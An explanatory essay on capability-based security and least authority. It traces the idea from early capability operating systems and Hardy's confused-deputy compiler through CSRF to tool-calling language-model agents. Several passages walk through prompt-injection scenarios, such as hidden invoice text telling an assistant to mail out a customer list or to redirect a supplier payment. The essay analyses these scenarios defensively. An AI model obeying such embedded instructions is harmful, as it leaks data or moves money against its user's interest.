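# Capability-based security and least authority for programs that call external services

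## What are capabilities, and what does least authority ask of a program?

Capability-based security controls what computer programs can do. On most systems, a program names a resource, such as a file, and the operating system checks whether the user who started the program may have it. On a capability system, the program must hold a capability, an unforgeable reference that both designates a resource and carries the right to use it. A program that holds no reference to a file cannot even request it. Levy (1984), in *Capability-Based Computer Systems*, lists a 1966 design on paper by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn at MIT as the first operating-system core of this kind. Capabilities are one way to follow the principle of least authority, the rule that a program should be able to bring about only what its task requires. The rule matters most for programs that run strangers' code or call outside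 services such as mail and banking, and researchers now apply it to programs in which a language model chooses the calls.

### The access matrix

Any form of access control has to settle which subjects may do what to which resources. A subject is whatever can receive rights of its own: a user account, a running program, or a single component inside a program. A resource is whatever needs protecting. Lampson (1971), in *Protection*, set the whole arrangement out as a grid, the access matrix, with a row for each subject (Lampson's word was "domain") and a column for each resource. Each cell holds the operations open to that subject on that resource. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, give a small example with three subjects and three files on a Unix machine:

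| | Account file (`/etc/passwd`) | Personal file (`/u/markm/foo`) | Login notice (`/etc/motd`) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | nothing |
| Bob | read | nothing | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

On a real machine the grid is enormous and most of its cells are empty, so storing all of it would waste space. Designers instead store the filled cells by column or by row. Storing them by column gives each resource an access control list, or ACL, of the subjects that may use it. The login notice's list would have two entries, "Bob: read" and "Carol: read". All the mainstream operating systems rely on some version of the ACL. Storing them by row gives each subject a capability list of the resources it may use, and each entry is a capability. Alice's list would have the entries "account file: read" and "personal file: write". People have long disagreed about whether the two methods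 are equivalent, because the grid shows who has which rights at one moment but not how rights pass from one subject to another.

Levy compares a capability to a ticket or a key. In a computer, it is a small data structure that holds an identifier for one object and a set of access rights. To add a line to a file, a program might call `PUT(file-capability, "this is a record")`. The first argument both identifies the file and establishes that the program may write to it. If programs could edit the bits of a capability, they could turn a right to read one file into a right to erase another. So the operating system or the hardware keeps the program's capabilities in a list, and the program refers to each one by its position. A program can still gain new capabilities (creating a file yields one), pass them to other programs, and make copies with fewer rights.

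Programmers use "capabilities" to mean a system's features, AI researchers use it to mean a model's skills, and *Agentao* (2026), a design for running language-model agents, uses it for the tools an agent can call. The security term is narrower than any of these.

### Opening a file in two ways

Suppose someone picks a letter from the "Open" dialog of a word processor. On today's systems, the dialog gives the word processor the letter's path name, a string of characters, and the word processor asks the operating system to open the file with that path name. The operating system checks whether the user may open the file, but it cannot check whether the user picked it. The word processor could have sent the path name of any other file the user owns, because any program can compose any string.

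The introductory essay *What Are Capabilities?* (Habitat Chronicles, 2017) describes the alternative. The word processor starts with no access to anything, including files, the network and devices. When the user picks the letter, the operating system, which usually supplies the dialog anyway, opens the file and gives the word processor a handle to it, which is a capability. The user sees the same dialog as before and answers no extra security questions. A malicious or faulty word processor can still ruin that letter, but it can't reach the user's other files or the internet.

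Programs usually rely on ambient authority, which Miller and colleagues define as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user". They compare it to a world where doors have no keys and open for anyone judged worthy. When a Unix program calls `open()`, it passes a file name but no credential, and the call succeeds or fails depending on the account the program runs under. Ambient authority can also lead to what Norm Hardy named the confused deputy, a program that serves two parties and uses one party's authority for the other's purpose. In one case, a customer got a compiler to overwrite its operator's billing records.

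A Unix program can receive a file either as a name or as a file that is already open. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained* (2003), contrast two commands that each copy one file into another, `cp foo.txt bar.txt` and `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`. In the first, the shell (the program that interprets typed commands) gives `cp` two names, and `cp` has to open the files itself. Since the user might type any names, the least authority `cp` can work with is all the authority the user has over the file system. In the second, the shell opens both files and gives `cat` two file descriptors, small numbers that stand for open files. Unix still runs `cat` with the user's full authority, as it does every program the user starts, so the second command is no safer in practice. However, the copy would still succeed if the system withheld everything except the two descriptors.

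### From least privilege to least authority

The rule behind all this is least privilege, and its standard statement is in a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. Nobody knew how to build a large system without flaws, so they offered eight design principles that tend to make flaws fewer and less serious. The sixth is that every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Their main reason was that this limits the damage from an accident or an error. It also reduces interactions among privileged programs and leaves fewer programs to audit when someone misuses a privilege. They gave the military rule of "need-to-know" as an example from outside computing.

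Two of Saltzer and Schroeder's other principles are often discussed with least privilege. Under fail-safe defaults, a program starts with no access and someone has to justify each grant. A mistake then usually causes a refusal, which people notice quickly, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions allows access it shouldn't and may go unnoticed for years. Complete mediation requires the system to check every access to every object. Saltzer and Schroeder regarded their eight principles as warnings, so a design that broke one deserved a second look.

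Mark Miller's doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition* (2006), separates two things that "privilege" might mean. Permission covers what a program may do directly to a resource. Authority covers every effect a program can cause, whether directly or through other programs that act on its requests. In Miller's example, a program called Alice has permission to write to the account file, and a program called Bob does not. But Bob may send messages to Alice, which writes whatever text Bob asks for into the file. Bob therefore has the authority to put any text in the file, even though Bob's row in the access matrix shows no permission to write to it.

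Miller thinks it unclear whether Saltzer and Schroeder meant permission or authority. Their tutorial concentrates on direct access, though they conceded that there seemed to be no conceptual reason to treat indirect access differently. Miller and other later writers prefer the term "least authority" because harm comes from effects, and someone who audited only permissions would judge Bob safe.

The preference has a price, which is that authority is much harder to establish. Anyone can read current permissions off the matrix. What Bob will eventually be able to bring about depends on how Alice and every other program in between behave, and no practical method computes that exactly. Miller works with bounds instead. Let EA be the set of pairs (subject, resource) in which the subject really will be able to affect the resource. Let TA be the set an analyst gets from the layout of permissions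 alone, by assuming that every program passes on whatever it can. Let BA be the set that remains after the analyst also takes into account the known behaviour of some trusted programs. Then

EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA.

Any pair missing from TA or BA is also missing from EA, so either set can reliably rule a pair out. TA is easy to compute, but checks based on it reject many harmless arrangements. BA is more useful. If Alice changes the account file only after checking that the request concerns the requester's own entry, an analyst who has read Alice's code can rule out most of the authority Bob would have under TA. Programs in the middle can therefore narrow authority as well as spread it, and much of the practical work on capabilities consists of writing small programs that narrow it.

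A second difficulty is timing. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro (2005), in *The Structure of Authority*, argue that security fails when it is treated as a separate concern, because whoever sets the rules in advance does not know the least authority a program will need. That becomes clear only when a user or another program makes a request. The user's choice of a letter in the dialog, for example, supplies the information that a permission table written in advance lacks.

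### How a language model calls a tool

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes agents as AI models that work on a user's behalf by calling tools in a loop. One of its examples is a request to find mentions of an event in recent emails, summarise what happened and save the summary to a file. The model only takes in text and produces text. An ordinary program around it, often called the harness, does everything else, including fetching the emails and saving the file.

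In each turn of the loop, the harness sends the model the user's request and a list of tools, each with a name, a plain-language description and a schema of its arguments. The model produces a tool call, which is structured text that names one tool and fills in its arguments, for example a mail search with the word "invoice". The harness parses the call and runs the matching function. If the function has to log in to a service, the harness supplies a password or access token from its own store. The harness then adds the result to the model's input, and the model either produces another call or writes its answer. Many harnesses reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that lets agents find and call tools on servers. These harnesses forward each call to an MCP server, which passes it to a service such as a mail system or bank.

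In Miller's terms, the model is Bob and the harness is Alice. The model has no permissions, but its authority includes everything its text can make the harness do. If the harness runs every well-formed call with the user's stored credentials, the model has all the authority those credentials allow. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), a proposal for coding agents, treats this as ambient authority and has the harness check each proposed call against a set of capabilities that the model never holds.

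The model's output also depends on whatever it has read, much of which other people wrote. Prompt injection is text in such material that steers the model towards an attacker's aim. It may be in an email, on a web page or in the description of a tool on someone else's MCP server. A filter that removed every instruction from outside material would also break useful behaviour. In an example from Christodorescu and colleagues, an agent summarising one entry in a bug tracker finds that the entry depends on another and sensibly summarises both. Training helps, but they point out that a guard that refuses improper requests 99% of the time still lets 1% through, and an attacker may be able to keep trying. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) therefore assumes that attackers can sometimes control the model and examines what the surrounding program does with the resulting tool call.

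### The invoice assistant

A small case brings these pieces together. The owner of a business asks an assistant to read the invoices in one mail folder and pay one supplier. The assistant is a language model inside a harness, and when the owner installed it, the harness received credentials for the whole mailbox, the business bank account and the company's file store. The task needs far less than that:

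| | What the task needs | What the program can do |
|---|---|---|
| Mailbox | Read the messages in the invoices folder | Read, send and delete mail in every folder |
| Bank account | Make one payment to one supplier for the sum due | Pay anyone any sum the account can cover |
| File store | Nothing | Read, change and delete every file |
| Duration | Until the payment goes through | As long as the stored credentials stay valid |

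Anyone who can get a message into the invoices folder can give the model text to read. Suppose one invoice contains white text on a white background with an instruction to send the company's customer list to an outside address. If the model follows the instruction, the harness can fetch the list from the file store and mail it out, and both services will accept the requests because the credentials are genuine. If the program had only the authority in the middle column, it could not carry out the instruction because it could not open the file store or send mail.

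That middle column is harder to fill in than it looks. Christodorescu and colleagues observe that a phone app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it, but an agent's needs are unknown until the user states a task, and they change with the next task. In the invoice task, some limits are unknown even after the user states the task. The owner can name the folder and the supplier at the start, but the sum due, and perhaps the supplier's account number, are written in the invoices. The limit on the payment therefore has to come from the same folder in which an attacker can leave a message.

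## Why does a program that serves two parties misuse its authority?

The invoice assistant works for its owner, but much of what it reads comes from other people. Programs were in this position long before language models existed. The standard example dates from about 1977, when a compiler overwrote billing records at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler turns source code into something a computer can run. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells the story with a few inessential details changed. The incident convinced Hardy, who already thought capabilities "neat and tidy", that they were necessary.

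### The compiler and the billing file

Tymshare's operating system protected files much as Unix does. The compiler was in a directory named SYSX, and customers started it by typing `RUN (SYSX)FORT`. They could also name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler ran with the authority of whoever started it, so it could write this output to any file the customer could write to.

Hardy and colleagues then had the compiler record which features of the programming language people used. It wrote these statistics to another file in SYSX, `(SYSX)STAT`, whose name was part of the compiler's code. The customer's authority did not cover that file, so the compiler needed authority of its own. Hardy's team gave it a "home files license", which allowed a program to write to files in its own directory.

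The billing records were also in SYSX, in `(SYSX)BILL`. A customer learned this name and entered it as the destination for debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file with that name. The operating system opened the file because the compiler had the home files license, and the compiler overwrote the billing records with debugging output.

It is hard to point to a faulty line of code. The compiler's code for writing debugging output was correct when its programmer wrote it, but Hardy says it became wrong when the compiler received the license. To foresee this, someone would have had to examine every place where the compiler wrote to a file, and even then the right change would not have been clear.

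### Repairs that fail

Hardy finds no check on the file name that would stop the compiler from misusing its authority. The compiler can't refuse every file in another directory, because customers have good reasons to send output there. It also can't refuse every file in SYSX, because the directory did not exist under that name when the programmer wrote the code, and someone with legitimate access to SYSX might want the output there. A rule against `(SYSX)BILL` alone would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to change the compiler whenever a new one appeared.

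Narrowing the license to the statistics file would protect the bills, but a customer could still type `(SYSX)STAT` as the destination and ruin the statistics. An access control list has the same problem, because the compiler has to be on the list for the statistics file, and the list does not record what each write is for. Least privilege therefore limits the loss here without removing its cause. Alan Karp, who works on the safety of AI agents, goes further in *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy* (2026), a mailing-list thread in which Miller posted a chatbot's account of the problem. He holds that least privilege solves other problems and has nothing to do with this one.

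Another proposed fix is for the compiler to check whether the customer may write to the file. Karp objects that a program often should not know what its requesters are allowed to do, and that giving it this information can violate company policy or the law, such as American rules on health records. Checking every write this way would also stop the compiler from updating the statistics, which it does for its operator, because the customer has no right to that file.

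Tymshare tried to fix this by adding a "switch hats" system call, which let a program choose between its two authorities before opening a file. The compiler could choose the customer's authority for debugging output, and a request to open the billing file would then fail. This worked for the compiler, but some other programs needed more than two authorities, and Hardy saw no obvious way to extend the call to kinds of authority that didn't involve files. The rules for opening a file already took fourteen "and"s and "or"s to write down. Each new permission made previously secure programs insecure, and each new restriction broke programs that people relied on.

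### Keeping the name and the right together

Hardy argues that the compiler went wrong because it had authority from two sources and could not keep them separate. Its programmers meant it to use the license for statistics and the customer's authority for debugging output. But it could request a file only by name, and the operating system allowed the request if either authority permitted it.

In a capability system, the operator gives the compiler a capability to the statistics file, and the customer gives it a capability to the file that should receive the debugging output. The compiler uses the operator's capability to write statistics and the customer's to write debugging output. A customer without a capability to the billing file can't give the compiler one, even if the customer knows the file's name. In the university lecture *Object Capabilities*, Heiser (2025) retells the story with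 the modern compiler `gcc`. The program contains a fixed capability to its log file and receives the destination as an argument. When Alice types the log's name as the destination, opening it fails because she has no capability to it.

Hardy had feared that capabilities would fill most of a system's storage. The systems Hardy's team later built were usually smaller than comparable ones with access lists, because capabilities replaced several separate mechanisms for naming and protection.

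Miller and colleagues make the general argument that if names and rights take separate paths through a system, some program has to rejoin them, and it may combine a name supplied by one party with a right belonging to another. In Karp's summary, a confused deputy "uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else".

A formal definition needs that last condition. Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, starts with a user U, a deputy D, and a privilege (o, r), meaning the right to perform operation o on resource r. The deputy is confused if

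(o, r) ∉ Priv(U), (o, r) ∈ Priv(D),

and D performs o on r as a consequence of U's request. Taken alone, this would also cover the compiler's normal work. Every customer who runs the compiler causes a write to the statistics file, which no customer may write to directly, and that is how the operator wants it. Gallo accordingly refines the definition to take account of who designated the resource.

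### Close's argument against access lists

Tyler Close turned Hardy's story into a case against access lists in general. Close (2009), in *ACLs Don't*, argues that they cannot produce correct decisions when more than two parties interact, because information that the decision requires gets lost as messages pass from one party to the next. Close gave a worked example that June on a mailing list for web standards. A photo site and a printing site both keep their files with the same storage service, and a user wants to print photo 123:

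1. The photo site asks the printing site to start a print job.
2. The printing site creates a file, job 123, at the storage service. It gives the photo site permission to write to the file and sends back the file's address.
3. The photo site asks the storage service to copy photo 123 into job 123. The service checks that the photo site may read the photo and write to the job file, and makes the copy.

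Now suppose the printing site is dishonest and sends back the address of photo 456, which belongs to the photo site. The photo site makes its usual copy request. The storage service checks that the photo site may write to photo 456, then overwrites it. The access list for photo 456 is accurate and does not include the printing site. But the request comes from the photo site, and nothing in it indicates that the printing site chose the destination.

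Ian Hickson replied in the same discussion that the photo site's mistake was to trust an address from a potentially hostile source. Close asked what check it should have made. The photo site could refuse the addresses of its own files, which would stop this attack, but that is the kind of file-name check Hardy rejected, and it would miss files that other people had allowed the site to edit. Close's alternative is to put an unguessable secret in each file's address, so that the address works as a capability. The three messages stay the same, but the printing site can't send the address of photo 456 because it doesn't know the secret.

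The same trick can expose secrets as well as destroy files. In a later example from Close (2010), a client copies data between two files by fetching one and sending its contents to the other. A dishonest storage service can give the client the address of a source file that the client may read but the service may not. The client then fetches the contents and sends them to the service.

### Cross-site request forgery

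The web's best-known confused deputy is the browser. When a user logs in to a site, the site usually gives the browser a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser attaches to later requests to that site. Pages from other sites can also make the browser send requests there. For example, a malicious page might contain a form that orders a transfer from the visitor's bank. If the visitor is logged in, the browser attaches the bank's cookie, so the order looks genuine to the bank. The attack, called cross-site request forgery (CSRF), works without the attacker seeing the cookie. Miller credits Kragen Sitaker with one of the earliest diagnoses of the confused deputy problem on the web, in August 2000.

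Waterken's *The Confused Deputy rides again!*, an essay from Close's project on web security, compares the browser to Hardy's compiler. The browser acts both for the user, with the user's passwords, and for the sites whose pages it displays, and nothing in a request shows which of them wanted it. *Cookies* (2026), the current draft of the web's cookie standard from the IETF, which sets internet standards, gives the same explanation. Cookies encourage sites to separate designation (in the web address) from authorisation (in the cookie), so a browser may supply the user's authorisation for an address that an attacker chose.

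The most popular defence is to put an unguessable value in every genuine form and refuse any submission without it. An attacker doesn't know the value, so the attacker's page can't include it. In effect, the form carries a small capability. The value does not stop clickjacking, in which an attacker lays an invisible copy of the genuine page over a game, so that the user presses a real button without seeing it. The Waterken essay proposes putting a secret in the page's address, which would prevent the attacker from loading the page at all.

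Other defences keep the cookie but limit when browsers send it. If a site marks a cookie "SameSite=Strict", browsers leave it out of requests from other sites. The IETF draft treats this as a robust defence but advises sites not to rely on it alone, since an attack can also start from a page within the site. The setting can also block legitimate visits. Someone who follows an emailed link to a private project page may get an error because the browser withholds the cookie needed to open it.

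The developers of Tahoe-LAFS, a file storage system, faced this problem. Tahoe-LAFS's *solve CSRF attacks by making references unforgeable, not by making them unshareable* points out that a forged request looks much like ordinary sharing. In both cases, one person sends a link or form, another clicks on it, and a site acts on the click. Defences that block the forgery therefore tend to block the sharing too. Tahoe-LAFS instead gave its files addresses that people can share but an attacker can't forge. However, the IETF draft calls the general approach "not a panacea", and anyone who obtains one of these addresses also gains access to the file.

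### Is an injected agent a confused deputy?

Many people now apply Hardy's term to agents. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, an audit of agent frameworks, has "confused-deputy failures" in its subtitle. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), an essay from the software security company Semgrep, makes the strongest version of the claim. It calls an agent under prompt injection a "classic confused deputy" and presents capabilities as the answer.

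Set beside the earlier cases, the invoice assistant from the last section does look familiar:

| | Compiler | Browser | Invoice assistant |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who chooses the target | A customer who types `(SYSX)BILL` | Whoever wrote the malicious page | Whoever hid text in an invoice |
| What authority permits the action | The home files license | The user's cookie | The owner's stored credentials |
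| Could the program's user do it directly? | No | Yes | Yes |

The last row is disputed. In *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, Siu, He and colleagues (2026) define the two attacks separately. In their confused deputy attack, a logged-in user asks for something that the agent may access but the user may not, such as every employee's salary. If R is the set of permitted accesses, then (user, target) ∉ R and (agent, target) ∈ R. In indirect prompt injection, the agent follows an instruction from an unauthenticated source, and the resulting action does not serve the user's task. By these definitions, the attack on the invoice assistant is only prompt injection, because the owner is entitled to mail out the customer list.

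But the same test would exclude cross-site request forgery, since the bank's customer is entitled to transfer the money. If the attacker counts as the person making the request, all three cases fit. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) takes this wider view and treats prompt injection as a variant of the confused deputy, in which untrusted content uses the human user's authority. This reading seems better, and it makes the browser a closer precedent for prompt injection than the compiler is.

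Even so, an attacker can do more to an agent than the customer could do to the compiler. The compiler was going to write debugging output anyway, and the customer chose only where. Text in an invoice may influence whether the model calls a tool, which tool it calls, and with what arguments. *Silent Egress* (2026), which examines agents that leak data after reading web pages, treats the user's intent as the source of ambiguity, whereas in the traditional cases it was unclear which party the program was serving.

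In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025), David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies. SQL injection is an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Developers can prevent it by sending the command and the text to the database separately. A language model has no such separation, because it predicts the next token (a short piece of text) from everything before it, instructions and data alike. David C therefore expects that developers can reduce the risk of prompt injection but may never eliminate it.

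### Choosing the wrong capability

In Semgrep's main example, a user asks an agent to summarize the first quarter's reports, and the agent receives a capability to read only the folder that holds them, for five minutes. One report contains an instruction to delete all files. The model produces a call to delete them, but the server refuses it because the agent has no capability for deletion. An attacker therefore can't reach a resource just by getting the model to write its name. The example is an illustration, not an experiment, but the reasoning is sound, and the protection doesn't depend on the model detecting the attack.

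Capabilities do not determine which of the available resources the model should use, or for what purpose. Suppose the business owner asks the assistant to pay two suppliers and gives it a payment capability for each, with a generous monthly limit because the sums are not yet known. A hidden line in the first supplier's invoice says that the second supplier has merged with it and that both bills are now payable to the same account. If the model acts on this, it pays the second supplier's bill with the first supplier's capability. No capability has been forged, and both the payee and the sum are within the limits. Siu and colleagues call this "capability misuse", and it can happen without an attacker. In their example, a cooking assistant asked only to suggest recipes looks up the user's medical records.

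Miller and colleagues anticipated this difficulty in 2003 by comparing capabilities to keys on a ring. Someone who picks a key for a known purpose before going to the door is fairly safe, but someone who tries every key on the ring may open the door with a key meant for something else. They suggest labelling each key with its purpose when it is received. In Hardy's compiler, the code matches each capability to its purpose, since the line that writes statistics always uses the statistics capability. An agent usually has no such line, so the model makes the match at each step. The harness can show the model a label, but the model reads it together with the attacker's text.

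The harness has to match each tool call to a capability, and it can make the problem worse if it searches its whole store for one that permits the call. Gallo proves that a system that selects authority this way, without regard to the request that led to the action, allows confused deputies even when nobody can forge its tokens. Close conceded a similar point in December 2009, while defending a proposal for browser requests that carry no automatic credentials. Jonas Sicking had objected that developers would simply write a library that added a security token to every request. Close agreed that poor design could bring the problem back, and quoted the proposal's advice that a permission should apply to one specific resource and never to "any identifier in this request". Semgrep's design partly follows this advice, because every tool call must specify which capability it uses, but the model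 still chooses that capability.

Gallo proposes tying authority to the request that started the work. Each step must continue the one before it and can use only privileges that were available at that earlier step, so Cᵢ₊₁ ⊆ Cᵢ, where Cᵢ is the set of privileges available at step i. An agent that serves two customers could then never use one customer's authority on the other's request. But the rule permits anything within the original grant. The owner's request included the right to pay both suppliers, so the rule would allow the misdirected payment.

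To catch that payment, a system must track the source of the content that prompted it. Surapani and colleagues describe two records that the system should consult together when the agent calls a tool. One shows who passed authority to whom, which determines what the agent may do. The other shows where each piece of content came from, which determines whether that content may trigger the action. Capabilities provide only the record of authority.

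David C recommends a simple rule, credited to a discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes information from a party, its privileges drop to those of that party. An assistant that had just read a stranger's email could do only what the stranger could. The rule would stop the hidden instruction to send out the customer list, but it would also stop the invoice assistant from paying anyone, since no supplier has the right to make payments from the owner's account.

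## How do operating systems and sandboxes give a program only chosen resources?

A program must request access to files, devices and the network from the operating system, which can refuse any of them regardless of who wrote the program or what text it has read. Designers have used capabilities to control this access since the 1960s, first throughout whole operating systems and later in sandboxes, which are closed environments for running one program or part of one.

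### The kernel's list

In Dennis and Van Horn's 1966 design, each running computation has a list of capabilities, or C-list. The core of the operating system, which they called the supervisor and later writers call the kernel, keeps this list where the program can't alter it. *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter of Levy's book, goes through the design in detail. A request works like this:

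1. The program asks for an operation and gives a number, for example "write" and 3.
2. The kernel looks up entry 3 in that computation's list, where it finds a pointer to an object and the rights that go with it.
3. If the rights include writing, the kernel carries out the request. Otherwise it suspends the program and starts an error handler in the computation that launched it.

The program can send any number, just as a Unix program can compose any file name, but the number only selects from the program's own list. If the list has five entries, a request for entry 40 fails. Entry 3 may be a file on one program's list and a tape drive on another's.

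A computation can also launch another one with fewer rights. The new computation starts with an empty list of capabilities, and the creator copies in some of its own, with reduced rights if needed. The creator can later stop the new computation, inspect it or take capabilities away. Dennis and Van Horn wanted this for debugging, so that an untested procedure couldn't destroy its author's files. Modern sandboxes set up a program in much the same way.

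The design includes protected procedures for code that serves other people. Someone who writes one can give others an "entry capability", which lets them call the procedure but not see or change anything it uses. The procedure runs with its creator's list plus one capability that the caller passes as an argument, so it can't reach the caller's other objects.

MIT built the first working version on a PDP-1, an early minicomputer, and students used it until the mid-1970s. The system had capabilities for only a few kinds of object, such as files, devices and queues. In 1967, a group at the University of Chicago began a more ambitious machine, whose hardware would check a capability at every memory access. They never finished it, but later designers used it as a model.

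### Hydra and the procedure call

Researchers at Carnegie-Mellon University built the Hydra operating system in the 1970s for a machine that joined up to sixteen small computers. Cohen and Jefferson's *Protection in the Hydra Operating System* sets out five principles behind the system, including least privilege.

Hydra applied this to every procedure call. When one procedure called another, the kernel built a fresh list of capabilities for the called procedure, combining those stored with it and those the caller passed to it. The called procedure could not use anything else the caller had. Hardy's remedy for the Tymshare compiler works the same way.

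Rights were a row of 24 bits, one for each kind of access. When a program stored a copy of a capability somewhere, it could supply a second row of bits as a mask, and the kernel kept only the rights present in both:

new rights = old rights AND mask.

Clearing a permission bit in a capability never let the holder do more, so a program could always weaken a capability safely before passing it on. For example, a user with read and write access to a file could leave a read-only copy of the capability in an object shared with a colleague.

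Hydra's users could also add new kinds of object, each with its own managing code. *The Hydra System*, another chapter of Levy's book, gives message ports as an example. A user's capability to a port does not let the user change the port's internal data. To send a message, the user calls a procedure belonging to the port manager and passes it the port capability and the message. The kernel checks that the capability is for a port, then gives the procedure a version with more rights so that it can record the message. Levy calls this rights amplification. It is a deliberate exception to the rule that capabilities only get weaker, and only whoever controls a type of object can set it up.

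The caller needed protection too, because the procedure might keep a capability and use it later. In Hydra, the caller could prevent this by removing one of the capability's rights. The procedure could still copy a file's contents into an object of its own, so Hydra had a second right to control that. If the caller's capability to the procedure lacked this second right, the procedure could change only objects that the caller had passed to it for that purpose. Researchers later argued at length about whether any capability system can guarantee such confinement.

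All this was slow because the PDP-11 processors in Hydra's machine had no support for capabilities. A program had to call the kernel to copy data out of an object before working on it, and again to put the data back. Auditing what a program could reach was also harder than reading its capability list, because objects could contain capabilities to other objects. Cohen and Jefferson point out that a program's real domain included everything it could reach by following those capabilities, as far as the rights they carried allowed.

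### From CAP to a kernel with a proof

Maurice Wilkes and Roger Needham's group at Cambridge built the CAP computer, which was running by the mid-1970s. Its processor checked capabilities in microcode, the lowest layer of its instructions, so programs used capabilities for ordinary memory access without calling a kernel each time.

KeyKOS grew out of work by Hardy's team at Tymshare and ran on IBM mainframes from 1983. It added persistence by saving the state of the whole machine to disk every few minutes, including running programs and their capabilities. After a power cut, programs resumed from the last save with the same capabilities. KeyKOS therefore rarely needed a start-up program with broad authority to open everything again by name, which most systems need because a restart wipes out their running programs.

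In the 1990s, Jonathan Shapiro at the University of Pennsylvania built EROS, a version of the KeyKOS design for ordinary Intel processors. Capability systems had a reputation for being slow, but EROS was largely as fast as Linux in tests of basic operations.

seL4 comes from a group in Sydney and is a very small kernel, with about 8,700 lines of C in its first verified version. File systems, network software and most device drivers run outside it as ordinary programs, and can affect each other only through capabilities. Programs even need capabilities to the memory that the kernel uses on their behalf, so one program can't exhaust the kernel's memory and stop the others.

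The seL4 kernel's main novelty was a machine-checked proof, completed by Gerwin Klein and colleagues in 2009, that its C code does what a formal specification requires. The proof rules out whole classes of error in the kernel, such as writing past the end of a buffer. Later proofs established that a program can change only what its capabilities permit, and that information does not leak between programs that a system's designer has separated.

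These proofs assume that the hardware behaves as specified. The original proof also assumed that the start-up code, a small amount of assembly code and the C compiler were correct. The group later removed the assumption about the compiler for some processors by checking the compiled program itself. The proofs about leaks don't cover timing, so one program might still learn about another from how long an operation takes. The proofs also don't establish that the capabilities were distributed sensibly. If a harness on seL4 had capabilities to both the customer list and the mail program, the kernel would be following its specification if it let the harness send the list to a stranger.

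### Why ordinary systems kept access lists

Windows, Unix and their descendants kept using access lists for several reasons, and it is hard to say which mattered most. One was that existing programs and their users identified files by name, so a capability system needs either new programs or a layer that imitates the older systems.

Access lists also suit administrators. An administrator can check the payroll file's list to see who can read it, and can remove a former employee by deleting an entry. In a simple capability system, someone would have to search every program's list of capabilities to do either. Saltzer and Schroeder raised both difficulties in 1975.

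Poor performance also hurt the reputation of capabilities. Intel's 1981 iAPX 432 processor protected objects in hardware and was much slower than the company's conventional chips.

Perhaps the strongest reason is that access lists addressed the threat on a shared computer of the 1970s, which was another user. Access lists separate users quite well, but they do little to separate two programs that the same user runs. This became a much larger problem once people were installing software from strangers, and it is the problem with a language model's tools.

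### Capsicum: capabilities inside Unix

Robert Watson, Jonathan Anderson, Ben Laurie and Kris Kennaway presented Capsicum in 2010 as a way to add capabilities to Unix without replacing it. They started from the file descriptors that Unix programs already use for open files. A descriptor works much like an entry in Dennis and Van Horn's list, but an ordinary Unix program can always get more of them by opening files by name. Capsicum lets a program give up that ability:

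1. The program starts with the user's full authority and opens the files, directories and network connections it will need.
2. It limits what each descriptor permits. An input file might allow reading but not writing, changing permissions or anything else.
3. It calls `cap_enter()` to enter capability mode. The program can't leave this mode, and any program it starts will be in it too.
4. From then on, the kernel refuses requests that use global names, such as file paths, network addresses and the identifiers of other programs. The program can use the descriptors it has. If one of them is for a directory, it can also open files inside that directory, but not above it.
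5. If the program later needs something else, another program outside the sandbox has to open it and pass in the descriptor.

This order matters because the risky work usually comes later. Capsicum's designers converted `tcpdump`, which displays network traffic and has to interpret packets that anyone may have sent. It opens the capture device first, so it could enter capability mode before reading any packets, and the basic change took two lines of code. But the program could then no longer look up the names of the machines in the traffic, because the lookup code needed to open files and connections of its own. It could also still read what the user typed in the terminal, because it had inherited the terminal's descriptor with all its rights. A few more lines of code limited those rights.

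They also converted Google's Chromium browser, the compression program `gzip`, and `dhclient`, which obtains a computer's network address. `dhclient` was easy to convert because its developers had already split it into a privileged part and an unprivileged part. Converting `gzip` took several hundred lines of code because the team had to move the compression into a separate process and pass it open files. Chromium already drew web pages in separate processes, and needed about 100 lines, compared with more than 22,000 for its Windows sandbox.

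Sandboxing slowed `gzip` only slightly, adding a little over 2 milliseconds to each run, mostly to set up the second process. That delay is noticeable for a tiny file, but for files of half a megabyte or more, the sandboxed version's speed was within about 5% of the original's. FreeBSD, a version of Unix, has included Capsicum by default since 2014.

Capsicum protects users from a program that an attacker takes over while it is running. It relies on the developer to make the program enter capability mode at the right moment, so it doesn't protect users from a malicious developer unless another program sets up the sandbox first.

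Watson also helped to start CHERI, a project at Cambridge and SRI International that puts capabilities into the processor. In an ordinary C program, a pointer is a number that gives an address in memory, and faulty code can produce any number. A CHERI pointer also records which stretch of memory it covers and what the program may do there, and a hidden tag bit marks it as genuine. If an ordinary instruction overwrites part of the pointer, the processor clears the tag and the program can no longer use the pointer. Cohen and Jefferson had mentioned using tags to store capabilities and data side by side, but their PDP-11s had none. Arm released a prototype CHERI processor, Morello, in 2022. CHERI can separate components inside one program, such as an image library from the browser that uses it. However, its pointers are twice the usual size, and developers have to recompile their software and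 sometimes alter it.

### WebAssembly and the host's handles

Many programs load plugins, which are code written by other people to add features. *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM* (Willison, 2026) explains that plugins for Datasette, a tool for publishing data, usually run with the application's full privileges, so a faulty or malicious one could break everything or leak private data. Willison wanted plugins that couldn't read unapproved files or use the network, so he turned to WebAssembly.

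WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs, originally designed for web browsers. A WebAssembly module can compute and use its own memory, but it has no instruction for opening a file or contacting a server. It can do these things only by calling functions supplied by its host, the program that runs it. If the host supplies none, the module can only turn inputs into outputs.

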